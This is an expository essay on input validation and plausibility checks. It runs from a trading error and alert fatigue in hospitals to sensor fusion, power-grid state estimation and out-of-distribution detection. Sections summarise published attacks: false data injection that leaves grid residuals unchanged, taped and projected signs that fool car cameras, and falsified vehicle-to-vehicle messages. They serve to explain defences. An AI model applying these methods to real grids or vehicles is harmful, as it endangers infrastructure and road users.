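On 2 May 2022, a trader at Citigroup's London-based trading firm meant to sell a basket of European shares worth $58 million. The order system had separate fields for the value in dollars and the number of units of a share index, and the trader typed 58 million into the units field. Each unit was worth about $7,684, so the order came to $444 billion. The *Final Notice* (2024) from the Prudential Regulation Authority, Britain's banking regulator, describes what happened next.

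The trader did check the order's value on the screen. The software should have multiplied the number of units by the index price, but the price feed was down, so the software used −1 as the price. The screen showed minus 58 million, and the trader saw the 58 million they expected. A rule that prices must be positive would have caught this. So would a form that made the trader enter a unit, because it would have rejected dollars in a field for index units.

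A pop-up then appeared with 711 warnings, 18 of them visible without scrolling. Sixty-five were hard blocks, which the trader could not override. The other 646 were soft blocks, and the trader overrode them all at once without having to read them.

The hard blocks applied to parts of the order, and none limited its total value. One of them blocked the order for any single stock if it was worth more than $2 billion. But the basket was spread over 349 stocks, so even at the mistaken size the average was about $1.3 billion per stock, and orders for 284 of them reached the trading algorithm. The Financial Conduct Authority, which fined the firm separately, values these orders at $189 billion, while the Prudential Regulation Authority gives $196 billion. Further controls suspended most of them, but the algorithm had sold $1.4 billion of shares by the time the trader noticed the mistake and cancelled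 the rest, about 15 minutes after entering the order.

Citigroup's New York desk had used a hard block on the total value of a basket for about nine years. The London desk had only a soft block, set at $100 million, and the software couldn't calculate the total without the missing price. The message at the bottom of the list read, "Due to lack of market data, Wave notional cannot be found." (Wave notional is the total value of the basket.) The order went ahead without its most important check. When data needed for a limit like this is missing, the system should stop the order until someone supplies the price.

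Unlike a soft block, a hard block on the total would have worked even if nobody read the warning. It would have been easy to justify, since this desk had no plausible reason to sell $444 billion of shares in one morning. Even a loose cap of $10 billion, more than 170 times the intended order, would have stopped the mistaken one.

### Alert fatigue

Hospital staff dismiss most of their warnings, much like the trader who dismissed 646 at once. *Benchmarking Drug Library Compliance and Alert Rates in Smart Infusion Pumps* (Souza, Mourad and colleagues, 2026) analysed 13.7 million infusions given at 90 institutions between 2014 and 2020. The pumps gave about one alert for every three infusions that used the dose limits. On average, staff overrode 92.9% of the alerts about doses beyond a soft limit and 97.8% of those about a sudden change.

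Alerts about sudden changes were less useful than soft-limit alerts, with about one in 46 leading someone to reprogram the pump, compared with one in 16. This may be because nurses often adjust a dose on purpose as a patient's condition changes, so a large change in dose is weaker evidence of a mistake than a large dose.

Souza and colleagues, who work for the manufacturer Baxter, count every hard block as a "good catch", so their figures can't show how many blocks stopped a real error. *Smart pumps improve medication safety but increase alert burden in neonatal care* (Melton, Timmons and colleagues, 2019) is a smaller study of three years of records from one unit for newborns. Hard limits stopped 160 attempts to give too high a dose, some of them 7 to 29 times the maximum. The researchers reviewed 20 of these attempts and found that 15 were true discrepancies. In the other five, the nurses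 had apparently set a high rate on purpose to fill the tubing quickly. Staff overrode 79% of the alerts at the soft upper limits, but cancelled or reprogrammed the infusion after the remaining 2,093.

Doctors also override many of the alerts in their prescribing systems. *Appropriateness of Overridden Alerts in Computerized Physician Order Entry* (Poly, Islam and colleagues, 2020) reviewed 23 studies, in which doctors overrode between 46.2% and 96.2% of alerts, and between 82% and 96.8% of alerts about doses.

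An override is a mistake only if the alert was right. In the studies that Poly and colleagues reviewed, experts judged between 43.9% and 88.8% of dose alert overrides to be reasonable. A high override rate can therefore mean that the limits are badly set. *Appropriateness of Alerts and Physicians’ Responses With a Medication-Related Clinical Decision Support* reports an extreme case in which only 28 of 382 alerts were clinically relevant, though the researchers had deliberately chosen drugs whose alerts doctors often overrode.

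Alert fatigue is the tendency to stop paying attention to warnings after seeing too many useless ones. Some evidence fits this explanation. *Understanding physicians' behavior toward alerts about nephrotoxic medications in outpatients* looked at alerts about drugs that are risky for people with weak kidneys. Doctors who had received more than 20 of these alerts overrode 90.5% of them, while the others overrode 70% on average. The doctors who received more alerts may just have had patients for whom the alerts were less useful. But reviewers found only 29.4% of 289 sampled overrides appropriate, so doctors were also dismissing many warnings that deserved attention.

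In one month, a single patient accounted for 75% of the alerts in Melton's newborn unit, mostly for two drugs. If a doctor has confirmed that a baby needs an unusually high dose, the pump could use a higher soft limit for that baby and keep the same hard limit. This would remove most of the repeated warnings and still stop a tenfold error. Citigroup's pop-up could also have been shorter, because hundreds of its warnings came from one mistake. A single line at the top showing the total value would have been more informative to the trader than the other 710 lines.

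### Limits learned from past data

Choosing all these limits by hand becomes impractical when a company has tens of thousands of fields, but software can draft the rules from past data. *Data Validation for Machine Learning* (Zinkevich, Polyzotis and colleagues, 2019) describes Google's system for checking the data that machine-learning models use. The system checks data against a schema, which lists the expected fields and the type and permitted values of each. It proposes a schema based on existing data, and engineers correct it. For example, it might propose that a country code has two letters or that an age is never negative.

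Meta already had rules of this kind when Shankar, Fawaz and colleagues (2023) set out to improve on them. Their paper, *Moving Fast With Broken Data*, calls schema checks necessary but not sufficient. A fault in a phone app might set a field to −1 or leave it empty, and a model that retrains every few hours could learn from the bad values before anyone fixed the app. Meta's engineers had tried an alert that fired when the share of filled-in values in a field dropped by more than 30%, but it raised so many false alarms that they silenced it and eventually abandoned the method.

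Fixed bounds also go out of date as behaviour changes. One remedy is to recalculate them every day from the previous week:

lowest accepted value = average of the last 7 days − z × standard deviation

highest accepted value = average of the last 7 days + z × standard deviation

The standard deviation measures how much the daily values vary, and z sets how strict the rule is. Such a rule adapts to slow growth but handles expected exceptions poorly, such as the sharp rise in shopping on Black Friday, an example from Shankar and colleagues. They designed a method that compares each new batch of data separately with several earlier days. It also groups fields that usually change together, so that one fault doesn't set off hundreds of alerts. In a trial on Instagram's data, the share of its alerts that were correct averaged 2.1 times that of an earlier method.

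A moving limit can also become too loose if errors enter the data used to calculate it. Suppose a company pays out about 100 prizes a day and uses a z of 3. A day with 1,000 payouts is far outside the limits, but if that figure gets into the record anyway, the seven-day average rises to about 229 and the standard deviation to about 315. The rule then accepts anything up to about 1,170, so the same mistake would pass the next day. To prevent this, the software has to leave a rejected value out of the calculation until someone confirms that it was genuine.

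Limits set by hand can also go out of date. One of Citigroup's later controls suspended trading in a stock when its price moved by a certain percentage. Staff raised the threshold from 5% to 15% in March 2020, when the pandemic made markets volatile, and nobody reviewed it until after the $444 billion order more than two years later. The newborn unit that Melton and colleagues studied kept its limits more current, reviewing them monthly and updating them four or five times a year. Even so, nurses ran 13% of infusions in a basic mode without dose limits, partly because the pump's list lacked many of the fluids they used.

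## Checking a reading against other sensors and physical models

A reading can satisfy every fixed rule and still be false. A speedometer stuck at 60 km/h shows a reasonable speed even when the car is stopped at a red light. The software has to compare the reading with other data, such as a satellite position that has stopped changing, to detect the fault.

### One signal, several signals, a model

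*A Plausibility-based Fault Detection Method for High-level Fusion Perception Systems* (Geissler, Unnervik and Paulitsch, 2020) divides checks into three levels, following earlier work on vehicle control. Single-signal monitoring compares one reading with fixed limits, like the range rule for a drug dose. Redundancy checks compare readings that should agree, such as camera and radar estimates of where the next car is. Model-based checks use a known relationship between quantities. For example, a report that a car is taking a tight bend at 150 km/h is almost certainly wrong, even though the bend and the speed are each plausible separately.

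Geissler and colleagues applied all three to roadside radars and lidars (sensors that measure distance with laser pulses), which help automated cars detect more distant objects. The system lowers an object's credibility if the object is more than 25 m long, moves faster than 80 m per second or appears away from any road on the map. It does the same for an object less than 2 m long and wide that moves faster than 20 m per second, because pedestrians and cyclists don't go that fast.

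When one sensor reports a car and a neighbouring sensor doesn't, the software first checks whether the second sensor could have detected it. If a lorry was in the way, the software doesn't treat the missing report as evidence that the car isn't there. To allow for such cases, it divides its belief between "exists", "does not exist" and "unknown". An impossible size adds to "does not exist", while an object reported from beyond a sensor's range adds to "unknown".

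A disagreement between sensors doesn't show which one is wrong. In a simulated row of 12 highway radars, Geissler and colleagues made one radar oversensitive, so that it reported objects that weren't there. Its neighbours then appeared to be missing objects, although they were working properly. At a simulated junction with two lidars, they blocked part of one lidar's view, as a splash of mud might, and the faulty sensor was the one that missed objects. With only two sensors, miss rates alone can't show whether one is missing objects or the other is reporting objects that aren't there. The researchers also assume that only one sensor fails at a time, which is reasonable for mud but not for an attacker.

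### The residual test

Many model-based checks use a residual, the difference between a measurement and the value a model predicted for it. For example, an aircraft's software might predict the aircraft's altitude from its last known altitude and rate of climb, then subtract that prediction from the new reading to get the residual.

| Step | Example |
|---|---|
| Predict | 1,000 m |
| Measure | 1,060 m |
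| Subtract | The residual is 60 m |
| Scale by the expected uncertainty | 60 ÷ 15 = 4 standard deviations, or 16 when squared |
| Compare with the threshold | 16 is above 3.84, so the reading fails |

The standard deviation of 15 m has to include uncertainty in both the prediction and the sensor. If their errors are independent, with standard deviations of 12 m and 9 m, the combined standard deviation is √(12² + 9²) = 15 m. If the errors also follow a normal distribution, the squared difference between reading and prediction, divided by 15², is below 3.84 for 95% of genuine readings.

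The scaled and squared residual is the squared Mahalanobis distance. For several measurements at once, the formula is:

d² = rᵀ S⁻¹ r

Here r is the list of residuals, and S is their covariance matrix, which records how uncertain each one is and how they tend to vary together. With a single measurement the formula reduces to the residual squared divided by the variance, which is 60² ÷ 15² = 16 in the example. The threshold rises with the number of measurements, to 5.99 for two. (Engineers also compute this distance on a neural network's internal features to score how unfamiliar an input is.)

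The covariance matters because errors are often correlated. An aircraft that has climbed faster than predicted should be higher than expected and still climbing faster than expected. Suppose the two residuals have a correlation of 0.9. If altitude and climb rate are both two standard deviations too high, d² is about 4.2 and the readings pass. If the altitude is two standard deviations too high and the climb rate is two standard deviations too low, d² is 80. Each reading is equally far from its prediction in both cases, but the second combination makes little physical sense.

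A 95% threshold rejects one genuine reading in 20, or one every two seconds at ten readings a second. Raising the threshold to 16 cuts this to about one in 16,000, or one every 26 minutes, but the test then accepts errors of up to 60 m instead of about 29 m.

A large residual can also mean that the prediction is wrong, for instance because the aircraft has flown into rising air. After rejecting a reading, a well-designed filter therefore continues from its own prediction but assigns it more uncertainty the longer it goes without a measurement. Once the combined standard deviation reaches 31 m, a difference of 60 m gives a d² of 3.7 and passes. A filter that treated its model as certain would keep rejecting true readings, just as no evidence can raise a prior of zero. But an attacker can still make a filter that follows its readings accept false ones by shifting them slowly enough to keep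 every residual small.

### False readings that fit the model

Power grids show a more basic limit. A control centre can't measure everything about a grid directly, so it estimates the grid's state from a larger number of meter readings. In the simplified model that Liu, Ning and Reiter (2009) studied in *False Data Injection Attacks against State Estimation in Electric Power Grids*, the readings are:

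z = Hx + e

The list z contains the readings, x is the unknown state, and e is the measurement error. The matrix H, which depends on the grid's layout and the electrical properties of its lines, gives the readings that each state should produce. The software finds the state x̂ that best fits the readings and raises an alarm if the residual, z − Hx̂, is too large.

Now suppose that an attacker chooses a false change in the state, c, and adds Hc to the readings, which is exactly what the meters would show if the state had really changed by c. The best estimate moves from x̂ to x̂ + c, and the new residual is:

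(z + Hc) − H(x̂ + c) = z − Hx̂

The attack leaves the residual unchanged, so neither a stricter threshold nor a better way of scaling the residual can detect it.

For example, in a network with one main line and two branches, each with its own meter, the two branch flows should add up to the main flow.

| Readings | Branch A | Branch B | Main line | Do they fit? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| True | 30 | 50 | 80 | Yes |
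| One meter falsified | 40 | 50 | 80 | No |
| A and the main line falsified | 40 | 50 | 90 | Yes |
| A and B falsified | 40 | 40 | 80 | Yes |

When only branch A's reading is false, the software can detect an error but can't tell which meter is wrong. If the meters are equally accurate, the best fit spreads the discrepancy of 10 evenly, leaving a residual of about 3.3 at each. An attacker who controls any two meters can make all three readings consistent with each other.

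Real grids have far more meters, but an attacker may need to tamper with only a few of them. Liu and colleagues simulated a standard test grid with 1,122 meters. In most cases, changing the readings of 10 meters was enough to put a chosen error into one chosen part of the estimated state.

These attacks are hard to carry out, as Liu, Ning and Reiter (2011) explain in a longer article with the same title. The attacker has to know the grid's current layout, which changes with maintenance and breakdowns and is normally known only to the control centre. Many of the meters are in guarded substations, and experienced operators may notice something odd. The model is also a linear approximation that becomes less accurate for large grids. But these are obstacles to getting hold of H and the meters, and the residual test does not stop an attacker who overcomes them.

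### What an independent measurement adds

In the toy network, protecting any two meters is enough, because their readings determine all three flows and the attacker can't change the third reading without causing a mismatch. If only the main meter is protected, the attacker can still raise one branch reading and lower the other by the same amount. *Detecting False Data Injection Attacks on DC State Estimation* shows more generally that protecting a set of basic measurements is necessary and sufficient to detect the attack that Liu and colleagues described. The paper also considers verifying some parts of the state independently.

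Extra sensors help much less if the attacker can change all their readings in one place. Drasar (2022), in *Perception of the Environment*, gives the example of a security program that inspects the computer it runs on. The program may use many tools to look for an intruder, but they all get their information from the operating system. If the intruder has altered the part of the operating system that supplies this information, more tools won't help. Only indirect evidence might reveal the intruder, such as evidence another computer could collect by monitoring network traffic.

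### A speed sign with tape on it

A car often has better evidence about the speed limit than the sign it reads. McAfee's *Model Hacking ADAS to Pave Safer Roads for Autonomous Vehicles* (2020) describes how researchers at the security company stuck a 2-inch strip of black tape on a 35 mph sign to lengthen the middle bar of the 3. The Mobileye cameras in two 2016 Teslas read the limit as 85. In a driving test, one car began to accelerate towards 85 mph, and the researchers braked well before it reached that speed.

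According to McAfee, the car in the demonstration sped up only when the driver double-tapped the lever to engage cruise control. A newer version of the camera, in a 2020 vehicle, did not make the mistake, although the researchers tested it only briefly.

A range rule would not have caught this error, because 85 mph is a real speed limit on a few miles of American road. A map showing a limit of 35 mph would have contradicted the reading. Even a map without speed limits would have contradicted it if the map showed the car on an ordinary street with junctions and driveways. Fortune (2020) reported that manufacturers were already adding map data for this purpose. Mobileye said in a statement carried by the Arkansas Democrat-Gazette that autonomous vehicles "will not rely on sensing alone" and would also use crowd-sourced maps.

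The map can also be wrong. At roadworks, a temporary sign may correctly show 35 where the map still has 65. Always obeying the lower limit would have defeated the tape, and driving too slowly usually does less harm than driving too fast. But a false low limit could then make the car brake hard on a motorway, which is also dangerous. *T2I-Based Physical-World Appearance Attack against Traffic Sign Recognition Systems in Autonomous Driving* (2025) reports road tests in which production cars passed altered signs and displayed either a 5 km/h limit or a warning of children crossing. The attack worked in 97% of the runs. The researchers recorded what appeared on the car's screen but did not test whether the car would brake.

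Some cars already use a simple physical model in which signs don't vanish as a car approaches. *Revisiting Physical-World Adversarial Attack on Traffic Sign Recognition* (2024) found that commercial systems commonly remember a sign until the car has passed its position, even if the researchers hid the sign for 20 to 60 seconds. This memory makes it harder to hide a real sign from the car, since one correct reading is enough, but it could also preserve a false reading that lasted only a moment.

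### Projected pedestrians and signs

A projector or a screen can create a false object without anyone touching a sign. In a test on a closed road, a Tesla Model X with its cruise control set to 18 mph slowed to 14 mph for a "phantom", an image of a pedestrian projected onto the road. In another test, a stop sign appeared for half a second in an advertisement on a television beside the car's path, and the car stopped in the middle of the road.

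Besides cameras, the Model X had radar and ultrasonic sensors, which cannot detect a projected pedestrian because it has no depth. The researchers who ran these tests think such cars act on the camera's detection even when the other sensors find nothing, to avoid missing a real pedestrian those sensors failed to detect. If a car brakes whenever any one sensor reports a person, adding sensors makes it less likely to hit someone but no less likely to brake for a phantom.

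The same researchers built a check called GhostBusters, which uses only the camera. Four small neural networks each examine one aspect of a detected sign:

- The context network sees the surroundings with the sign itself removed, and judges whether a sign belongs there.
- The surface network looks for textures that a sign wouldn't have, such as bricks or leaves showing through a projection.
- The light network looks for unnatural brightness.
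- The depth network uses the way the scene shifts between frames as the car moves.

A fifth network combines their outputs. An attacker can avoid the brick texture by projecting onto a smooth wall, but the middle of a wall is an odd place for a road sign. In tests, GhostBusters caught 99.4% of phantom signs at a setting that produced no false alarms, compared with 97.6% for a single network trained on the same task.

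The result of no false alarms comes from a test set of 5,108 images taken at night. Even if every image had shown a real sign, the true rate could still be about one false alarm in 1,700 signs. At that rate, a car that passes hundreds of signs a day would ignore a real one every week or so.

These checks test whether a sign is physically real. If someone puts up a real board with a written command on it, the checks can't show whether that person had any authority over the car.

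### Objects reported by other cars

Lidar can test whether anything solid is where an object is supposed to be. Hurl, Cohen and colleagues (2019), in *TruPercept*, used this to check the reports that cars send each other about objects they have detected. The software takes the laser points in a narrow region around the line from the car to the centre of the reported object. If more than 10% of these points are closer to the car than that centre, the report is plausible, because the laser has hit either the object or something in front of it. If nearly all are further away, the laser has passed through the place where the object should be.

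The researchers tried this on a scene from a video game. A pedestrian was stepping out from behind a parked truck, where the car's own sensors couldn't detect them. An oncoming car reported the pedestrian, but also reported a false object less than 10 m ahead. When the software simply combined the reports, it kept both. The lidar test removed the false object and kept the pedestrian. The test would not have removed a false object that the oncoming car reported behind the truck, since the truck would block the laser there too.

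Success in one scene didn't carry over to ordinary traffic. Hurl and colleagues measured average precision, a score that rewards finding real objects and penalises false ones. For cars at all distances, a vehicle using only its own sensors scored 36.3%. Three methods of adding other vehicles' reports scored between 31.5% and 36.7%. The best method mainly used the vehicle's own detections, and accepted another vehicle's report only when few of its own laser points fell on the object and the report passed the plausibility test. Performance fell significantly when a tenth of the vehicles reported the same kind of false obstacles in front of one car.

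### Messages about position and speed

Cars can also broadcast their position, speed and heading. A digital signature proves who sent such a message and that nobody changed it in transit, but a legitimate sender can still lie, as Gaber, Wahid and colleagues (2026) point out in *Attack Injection to Vehicle Reactions*. *Deep Reinforcement Learning for Misbehavior Detection Under Partially Observable V2X Data* (2026) tests detectors on five kinds of false message from VeReMi, a widely used collection of simulated traffic data. Different comparisons can expose these false messages.

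| False message | What can expose it |
|---|---|
| The same position every time | A reported speed above zero |
| A random position every time | Jumps that no car could make |
| A random speed every time | Positions that imply a different speed |
| The true position plus a fixed offset | A camera, radar or map |
| True data sent late | An old timestamp, or the receiver's own sensors |

The fixed offset resembles the attack on the power grid. If a car reports every position 20 m too far forward, its speed, heading and successive positions all agree, so no model of its motion will detect the offset. The receiver has to observe the car with its own sensors, or find that the reported position is off the road, for example in a field.

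When the receiver can't see the sender, it may have to compare messages from several cars. *SafeCoop* (2025) describes a system in which a language model checks whether each message contradicts the majority, conflicts with what the receiving car sees, or changes suddenly from the sender's previous message. The majority check works on isolated outliers, but one of the attacks the researchers consider can defeat it, so they added the comparison with the receiving car's own view.

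Weighting the messages can help if the weights don't come from the attackers. In Abasıkeleş-Turgut's *From Trust Scores to Driver Decisions* (2026), simulated cars decide whether a reported hazard is real, giving more weight to recent reports and to those from senders who are trusted or close to the hazard. If the evidence is too evenly balanced, a car waits for more reports and makes its best guess only when it reaches the hazard. Waiting reduced missed hazards from 10.6% to 9.5% and unnecessary detours from 9.7% to 8.0%, compared with deciding at once by the same method.

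But the senders report their own positions. When a quarter of the cars were attackers who falsely claimed to be next to the hazard, the system missed 12.7% of hazards, while an older method that ignored position missed 11.6%. Abasıkeleş-Turgut adds an optional check that lets the receiver partly measure the sender's position, by comparing the claimed position with the radio's range and with a separate estimate of the sender's distance.

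A filter for such messages can also discard true warnings. In simulated traffic in Berlin and Boston, *CATS* (2025) compared a new filter with two settings of a system based on senders' reputations. The setting meant to catch the most bad messages let through 257 times as many of them as the new filter did. But the new filter discarded three times as many good messages as the setting meant to lose the fewest. The researchers consider this a reasonable trade for safety. That depends on which good messages the filter discards, since one of them may be the only warning of a crash around the bend.

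Even a perfect check of each message wouldn't stop all the effects of a false one. Gaber and colleagues simulated 1,870 vehicles, a fifth of which could carry out attacks from a library of 76. In one recorded sequence, a car changed its speed because of a false message and then truthfully broadcast its new movement, and another car reacted to that broadcast. The broadcast would have passed any comparison with radar, a map or the laws of motion because it was true.

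## Learned scores for unfamiliar inputs

Limits, formulas and extra sensors work only where an engineer knows what to compare an input with. There may be nothing to compare it with if the input is a photograph of an unknown object or a request in words nobody anticipated. An out-of-distribution (OOD) detector instead uses the numbers a trained model computes for an input to score how familiar the input is, and flags it if the score falls below a threshold.

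Engineers usually set the threshold with familiar data alone. They score some genuine inputs that the model did not see in training, and pick the value that 95% of them exceed. The method's main advantage is that it needs no examples of strange inputs, which nobody can collect in full. However, the detector flags one genuine input in 20.

### Four ways to score an input

Suppose an image classifier knows three classes: cats, dogs and horses. For each class it computes a number called a logit, f, which is higher the better the image fits the class. The softmax function turns the logits into probabilities that add up to one:

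p(class k) = exp(f_k) ÷ Σ exp(f_i)

The oldest score, softmax confidence, is the largest of these probabilities. Liu, Owens and colleagues (2020), in *Energy-based Out-of-distribution Detection*, proposed using the logits directly, in a quantity called energy:

E = −log Σ exp(f_i)

Low energy counts as familiar. The two scores can disagree completely:

| Logits | Softmax confidence | Energy |
|---|---|---|
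| (10, 0, 0) | 0.9999 | −10 |
| (3, −7, −7) | 0.9999 | −3 |

The lower row is the upper row with 7 subtracted from every logit. Softmax depends only on the differences between logits, so the confidence stays the same, while the energy rises by 7. The upper image fits "cat" very well, while the lower one fits it weakly but fits the other classes even worse. With an energy threshold of −5, the system would accept the upper image and flag the lower one.

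Liu and colleagues found a similar pair in real data. A classifier trained on CIFAR-10, a set of small photographs of animals and vehicles, gave one of those photographs a confidence of 1.0 and a picture of a house number 0.99. The photograph had an energy of −11.19, and the house number had an energy of −7.11. Over six sets of unfamiliar images, the detector wrongly accepted 51% of the images using softmax confidence and 33% using energy.

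Ordinary training does not guarantee this gap. It rewards correct probabilities, and adding the same number to every logit changes the energy but leaves the probabilities unchanged. Liu and colleagues therefore also trained the classifier on a large collection of outside images to raise their energy, and the share of unfamiliar images wrongly accepted fell to about 3%.

A detector can also use features, the numbers from which the classifier computes its logits. It averages the features of each class in the training data, then measures the Mahalanobis distance (the distance used in the residual test) from a new input's features to the nearest average. If the distance is large, the detector treats the input as unfamiliar.

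The remaining method needs no classes. A generative model learns how probable each input is, and the detector flags inputs with a low likelihood, p(x). This method can fail badly, although it seems the most natural of the four.

### How well the scores work

Researchers compare detectors with AUROC, which here measures how well they rank familiar inputs above unfamiliar ones, with 0.5 equivalent to guessing. They also use FPR@95 ("false positive rate at 95%"). Many of these papers treat familiar inputs as the positives, so FPR@95 is the share of unfamiliar inputs that a detector accepts when it accepts 95% of familiar ones. The name is confusing because this is the detector's miss rate, and its false-alarm rate is fixed at 5%. The calculation can also be reversed to give the share of familiar inputs flagged when the detector catches 95% of unfamiliar ones. Guessing scores 95% on both versions.

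The miss rate varies widely with the kind of unfamiliar input. Rozumnyi, Suchánek and colleagues (2026), in *Fi-ImageNet-1k*, tested 21 detectors on a strong classifier that sorts images into the 1,000 classes of ImageNet, a standard collection of photographs. The lowest miss rate was 1.2% on pictures of unfamiliar plants and 65% on a new set of 655 images. These images came from ImageNet itself, where annotators had put them in classes that didn't fit. One showed a Denison barb, a small striped fish, labelled "electric ray".

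The same researchers also tested models that match images with words, which can compare a picture with names both inside and outside the 1,000 classes. The score is the share of the picture's total similarity that falls on the known names, much as Bayes' rule divides probability among explanations. Without extra names, eight such models missed an average of 78% of the 655 images. They missed 59% when a language model supplied about 20 similar names for each class, and 14% when the researchers supplied the correct names. The models could therefore recognise most of the unfamiliar objects, but only if the list included the correct names.

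Learned scores have worked less well in other fields. In *MOOD* (2026), a benchmark for models that predict the properties of materials, every detector without labelled examples of unfamiliar data had a median AUROC within 0.01 of the 0.5 expected from guessing, across 264 settings. *Dataset Identity, Not Novelty* (2026) notes that no detector performs best on all pairs of familiar and unfamiliar datasets. A developer therefore can't safely choose a detector from a published ranking without testing it on the kinds of unfamiliar input the system is likely to receive.

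A detector can score poorly because the test is flawed. In *Decodable but Not Detectable*, Balachandran (2026) investigated an AUROC of 0.326, far worse than guessing, on a set of business documents. The test treated memos as unfamiliar, but the model had trained on memos, so the detector correctly scored them as familiar. After Balachandran removed the memos and retrained the model, the AUROC rose to 0.911.

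### Why a high likelihood does not mean familiar

Nalisnick, Matsukawa and colleagues (2018), in *Do Deep Generative Models Know What They Don't Know?*, trained a generative model on CIFAR-10 and then gave it SVHN, a set of photographs of house numbers. They expected the model to assign the house numbers a lower likelihood than the CIFAR-10 images, but it assigned them a higher one.

Likelihood is given here in bits per dimension, roughly the number of bits the model needs to encode each value in an image, so fewer bits mean a higher likelihood. New CIFAR-10 photographs needed 3.46 bits, while images of house numbers needed only 2.39. Each image has 3,072 values, so the average gap is about 3,300 bits per image. This corresponds to a likelihood about 2 to the power 3,300 times higher for the house numbers, which should have scored lower than the photographs.

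Similarly, a model trained on pictures of clothes gave handwritten digits a higher likelihood than new pictures of clothes. Two other types of generative model behaved the same way. But a model trained on house numbers did not give CIFAR-10 images a higher likelihood than house numbers.

The most likely input can be a strange one. If a coin lands heads 60% of the time, the most likely sequence of 1,000 tosses is all heads, but nobody will ever see it because vastly more sequences have about 600 heads. *Detecting Out-of-Distribution Inputs to Deep Generative Models Using Typicality* (2019) gives the example of a bell-shaped distribution of images centred on a plain grey picture. The grey picture has the highest density, yet random samples never look like it. This suggests flagging inputs with unusually high likelihood as well as those with low likelihood. *Further Analysis of Outlier Detection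 with Deep Generative Models* (2020) warns that such a test is hard to extend beyond simple distributions.

Another explanation is that house numbers are simpler pictures. If q is the distribution of the new data and p is the model, then:

average log-likelihood = −H(q) − KL(q ‖ p)

H(q) is the entropy of the new data, a measure of how varied and unpredictable they are. KL(q ‖ p) is a penalty for the mismatch between the data and the model, and is zero only if the two distributions are the same. Simple data have low entropy, which can outweigh a large penalty.

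The figures from Nalisnick and colleagues allow a rough check. A model trained on images of house numbers needed 2.06 bits per color value to encode such images, so their entropy is at most about 2.06 bits per value. The model trained on CIFAR-10 needed 2.39 bits, so its mismatch with the house-number images added at least 0.33 bits per value, or about 1,000 bits per image. These extra bits were hidden in the total because the images are simple and take few bits to encode.

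Kamkari, Ross and colleagues (2024), in *A Geometric Explanation of the Likelihood OOD Detection Paradox*, explain how a model can give house numbers such high density without ever generating one. Simple images can vary in fewer directions, so they may occupy a region with very little volume. Because probability is density multiplied by volume, the total probability of that region can be close to zero even when its density is high. Their detector accepts an input only if its likelihood is high and the model allows many directions of variation around it. It equalled or beat the best detectors that used the same models. However, *Resultant* (2024) lists several of these explanations and calls the fundamental reasons unresolved.

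Bayes' rule shows what the likelihood leaves out:

odds that x is unfamiliar = prior odds × p(x | unfamiliar) ÷ p(x | familiar)

A generative model of familiar data supplies only the last term. Li, Lu and colleagues (2025) show in *Out-of-Distribution Detection Methods Answer the Wrong Questions* that even a perfect model of familiar data can be the wrong tool. In their one-dimensional example, familiar readings follow a bell curve around 0 and unfamiliar ones a bell curve around 2. The correct model of the familiar readings gives −2 and 2 the same score, although −2 is almost certainly familiar, and its AUROC is about 0.86. A deliberately wrong model, centred far to the left, scores readings as more unfamiliar the further right they lie. Its AUROC is about 0.92, the best possible.

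In the house-number case, comparing the two models would easily identify the house-number images, by a margin of about 1,000 bits per image on average. But that requires a model of house numbers, so someone must have anticipated them as inputs.

### What familiar data alone can teach

Theory puts this limit more exactly. Fang, Li and colleagues (2024), in *On the Learnability of Out-of-distribution Detection*, extend a paper of theirs from 2022 on when a training method that sees only familiar data can learn to detect unfamiliar data. They call detection learnable if, for n training examples:

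expected value of [R(trained detector) − R(best available detector)] ≤ ε(n), with ε(n) shrinking to zero

R is the average loss from mistakes on a mixture of familiar and unfamiliar inputs. The same ε(n) has to work for every mixture the detector might receive.

Fang and colleagues prove that this is impossible if the possible mixtures include all those in which familiar and unfamiliar inputs overlap. For example, a bank's assistant might learn from customers' messages, including "cancel it", which refers to a card. In one town, the only unfamiliar messages are about holidays, so the best detector accepts "cancel it". In another, a gym has printed the bank's number by mistake, and most people who write "cancel it" mean their gym membership, so the best detector rejects it. The training data are the same in both towns, so the training method produces the same detector, which can't be the best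 one in both.

Even without overlap, detection isn't always learnable. For a standard type of neural network, Fang and colleagues show that it is learnable if and only if the number of possible inputs is finite. Digital images meet this condition because each pixel has a limited number of values, but the guarantee concerns what happens as the training data grow without limit. Detection is also learnable for images that differ clearly from the familiar ones in both content and style, which fits the low miss rate for plants. Fang and colleagues conclude that different situations need different detectors.

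In *A Closer Look at the Learnability of Out-of-Distribution (OOD) Detection*, Garov and Chaudhuri (2025) consider these results too pessimistic because detection often works reasonably well in practice. They relax the definition of learnability so that, roughly speaking, the amount of data needed may differ between problems, and several of the impossible cases become possible. This doesn't help the bank, whose problem is that the messages themselves are identical.

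### Strange to the model, or from somewhere else

Li and colleagues object more broadly that detectors built on classifiers don't measure whether an input comes from a different source than the training data, which is what their users want to know. Softmax confidence and energy measure the model's certainty about which known class fits, and feature distance measures how unusual the input is in terms of features learned only to separate those classes. Better formulas can't fix this if the model never learned what makes the unfamiliar input different.

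In one experiment, a classifier was trained on images of aeroplanes, cats and trucks, then tested on dogs. Feature distance separated the dogs from the familiar images with an AUROC of only 0.537. Training had never required the classifier to tell cats from dogs, so its features for the two overlapped almost entirely.

Scores based on uncertainty can flag familiar inputs and miss unfamiliar ones. A photograph with several objects is familiar but has no single right label, and these scores separated such photographs from unfamiliar ones with an AUROC of only about 0.6. A text test used a model trained to judge whether one sentence follows from another. When set to accept 95% of familiar sentence pairs, the detectors also accepted more than 95% of the pairs from one outside dataset and more than 92% from another, which is about as good as guessing.

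The usual remedies only partly work. Li and colleagues gave a classifier for keyboards and porcupines an extra "other" class, with cups and skyscrapers as examples. It then put bottles and cans in that class, but not hamsters and mice. Training on outside images, as in the energy experiment, improved detection of most new classes but lowered accuracy by more than 10% when familiar objects appeared in altered conditions. Larger models did better, but the features of even one trained on internet-scale data left over 5% error on a hard test, whatever the scoring method.

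Denipitiyage, Menon and colleagues (2026), in *Mining the Shadows*, give a more hopeful analysis, although they also say that the best detectors on a standard benchmark still flag about 30% of familiar images as unfamiliar. They look at the scores of the classes the classifier did not choose. If it labels a picture "dog" but gives low scores to wolves and coyotes, the picture is probably unfamiliar. They prove, for a simplified classifier, that this signal exists if unfamiliar inputs share features with one known class but lack the features that class shares with related classes.

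Strengthening the signal in training cut the miss rate for similar-looking unfamiliar images from 61% to 30% when the familiar data were CIFAR-10. With the 100 classes of CIFAR-100, the miss rate fell only from 55% to 53%. The method would also do little to help detect the dogs in the experiment by Li and colleagues, because a classifier trained to recognise cats, aeroplanes and trucks has no other animal class whose score could look wrong.

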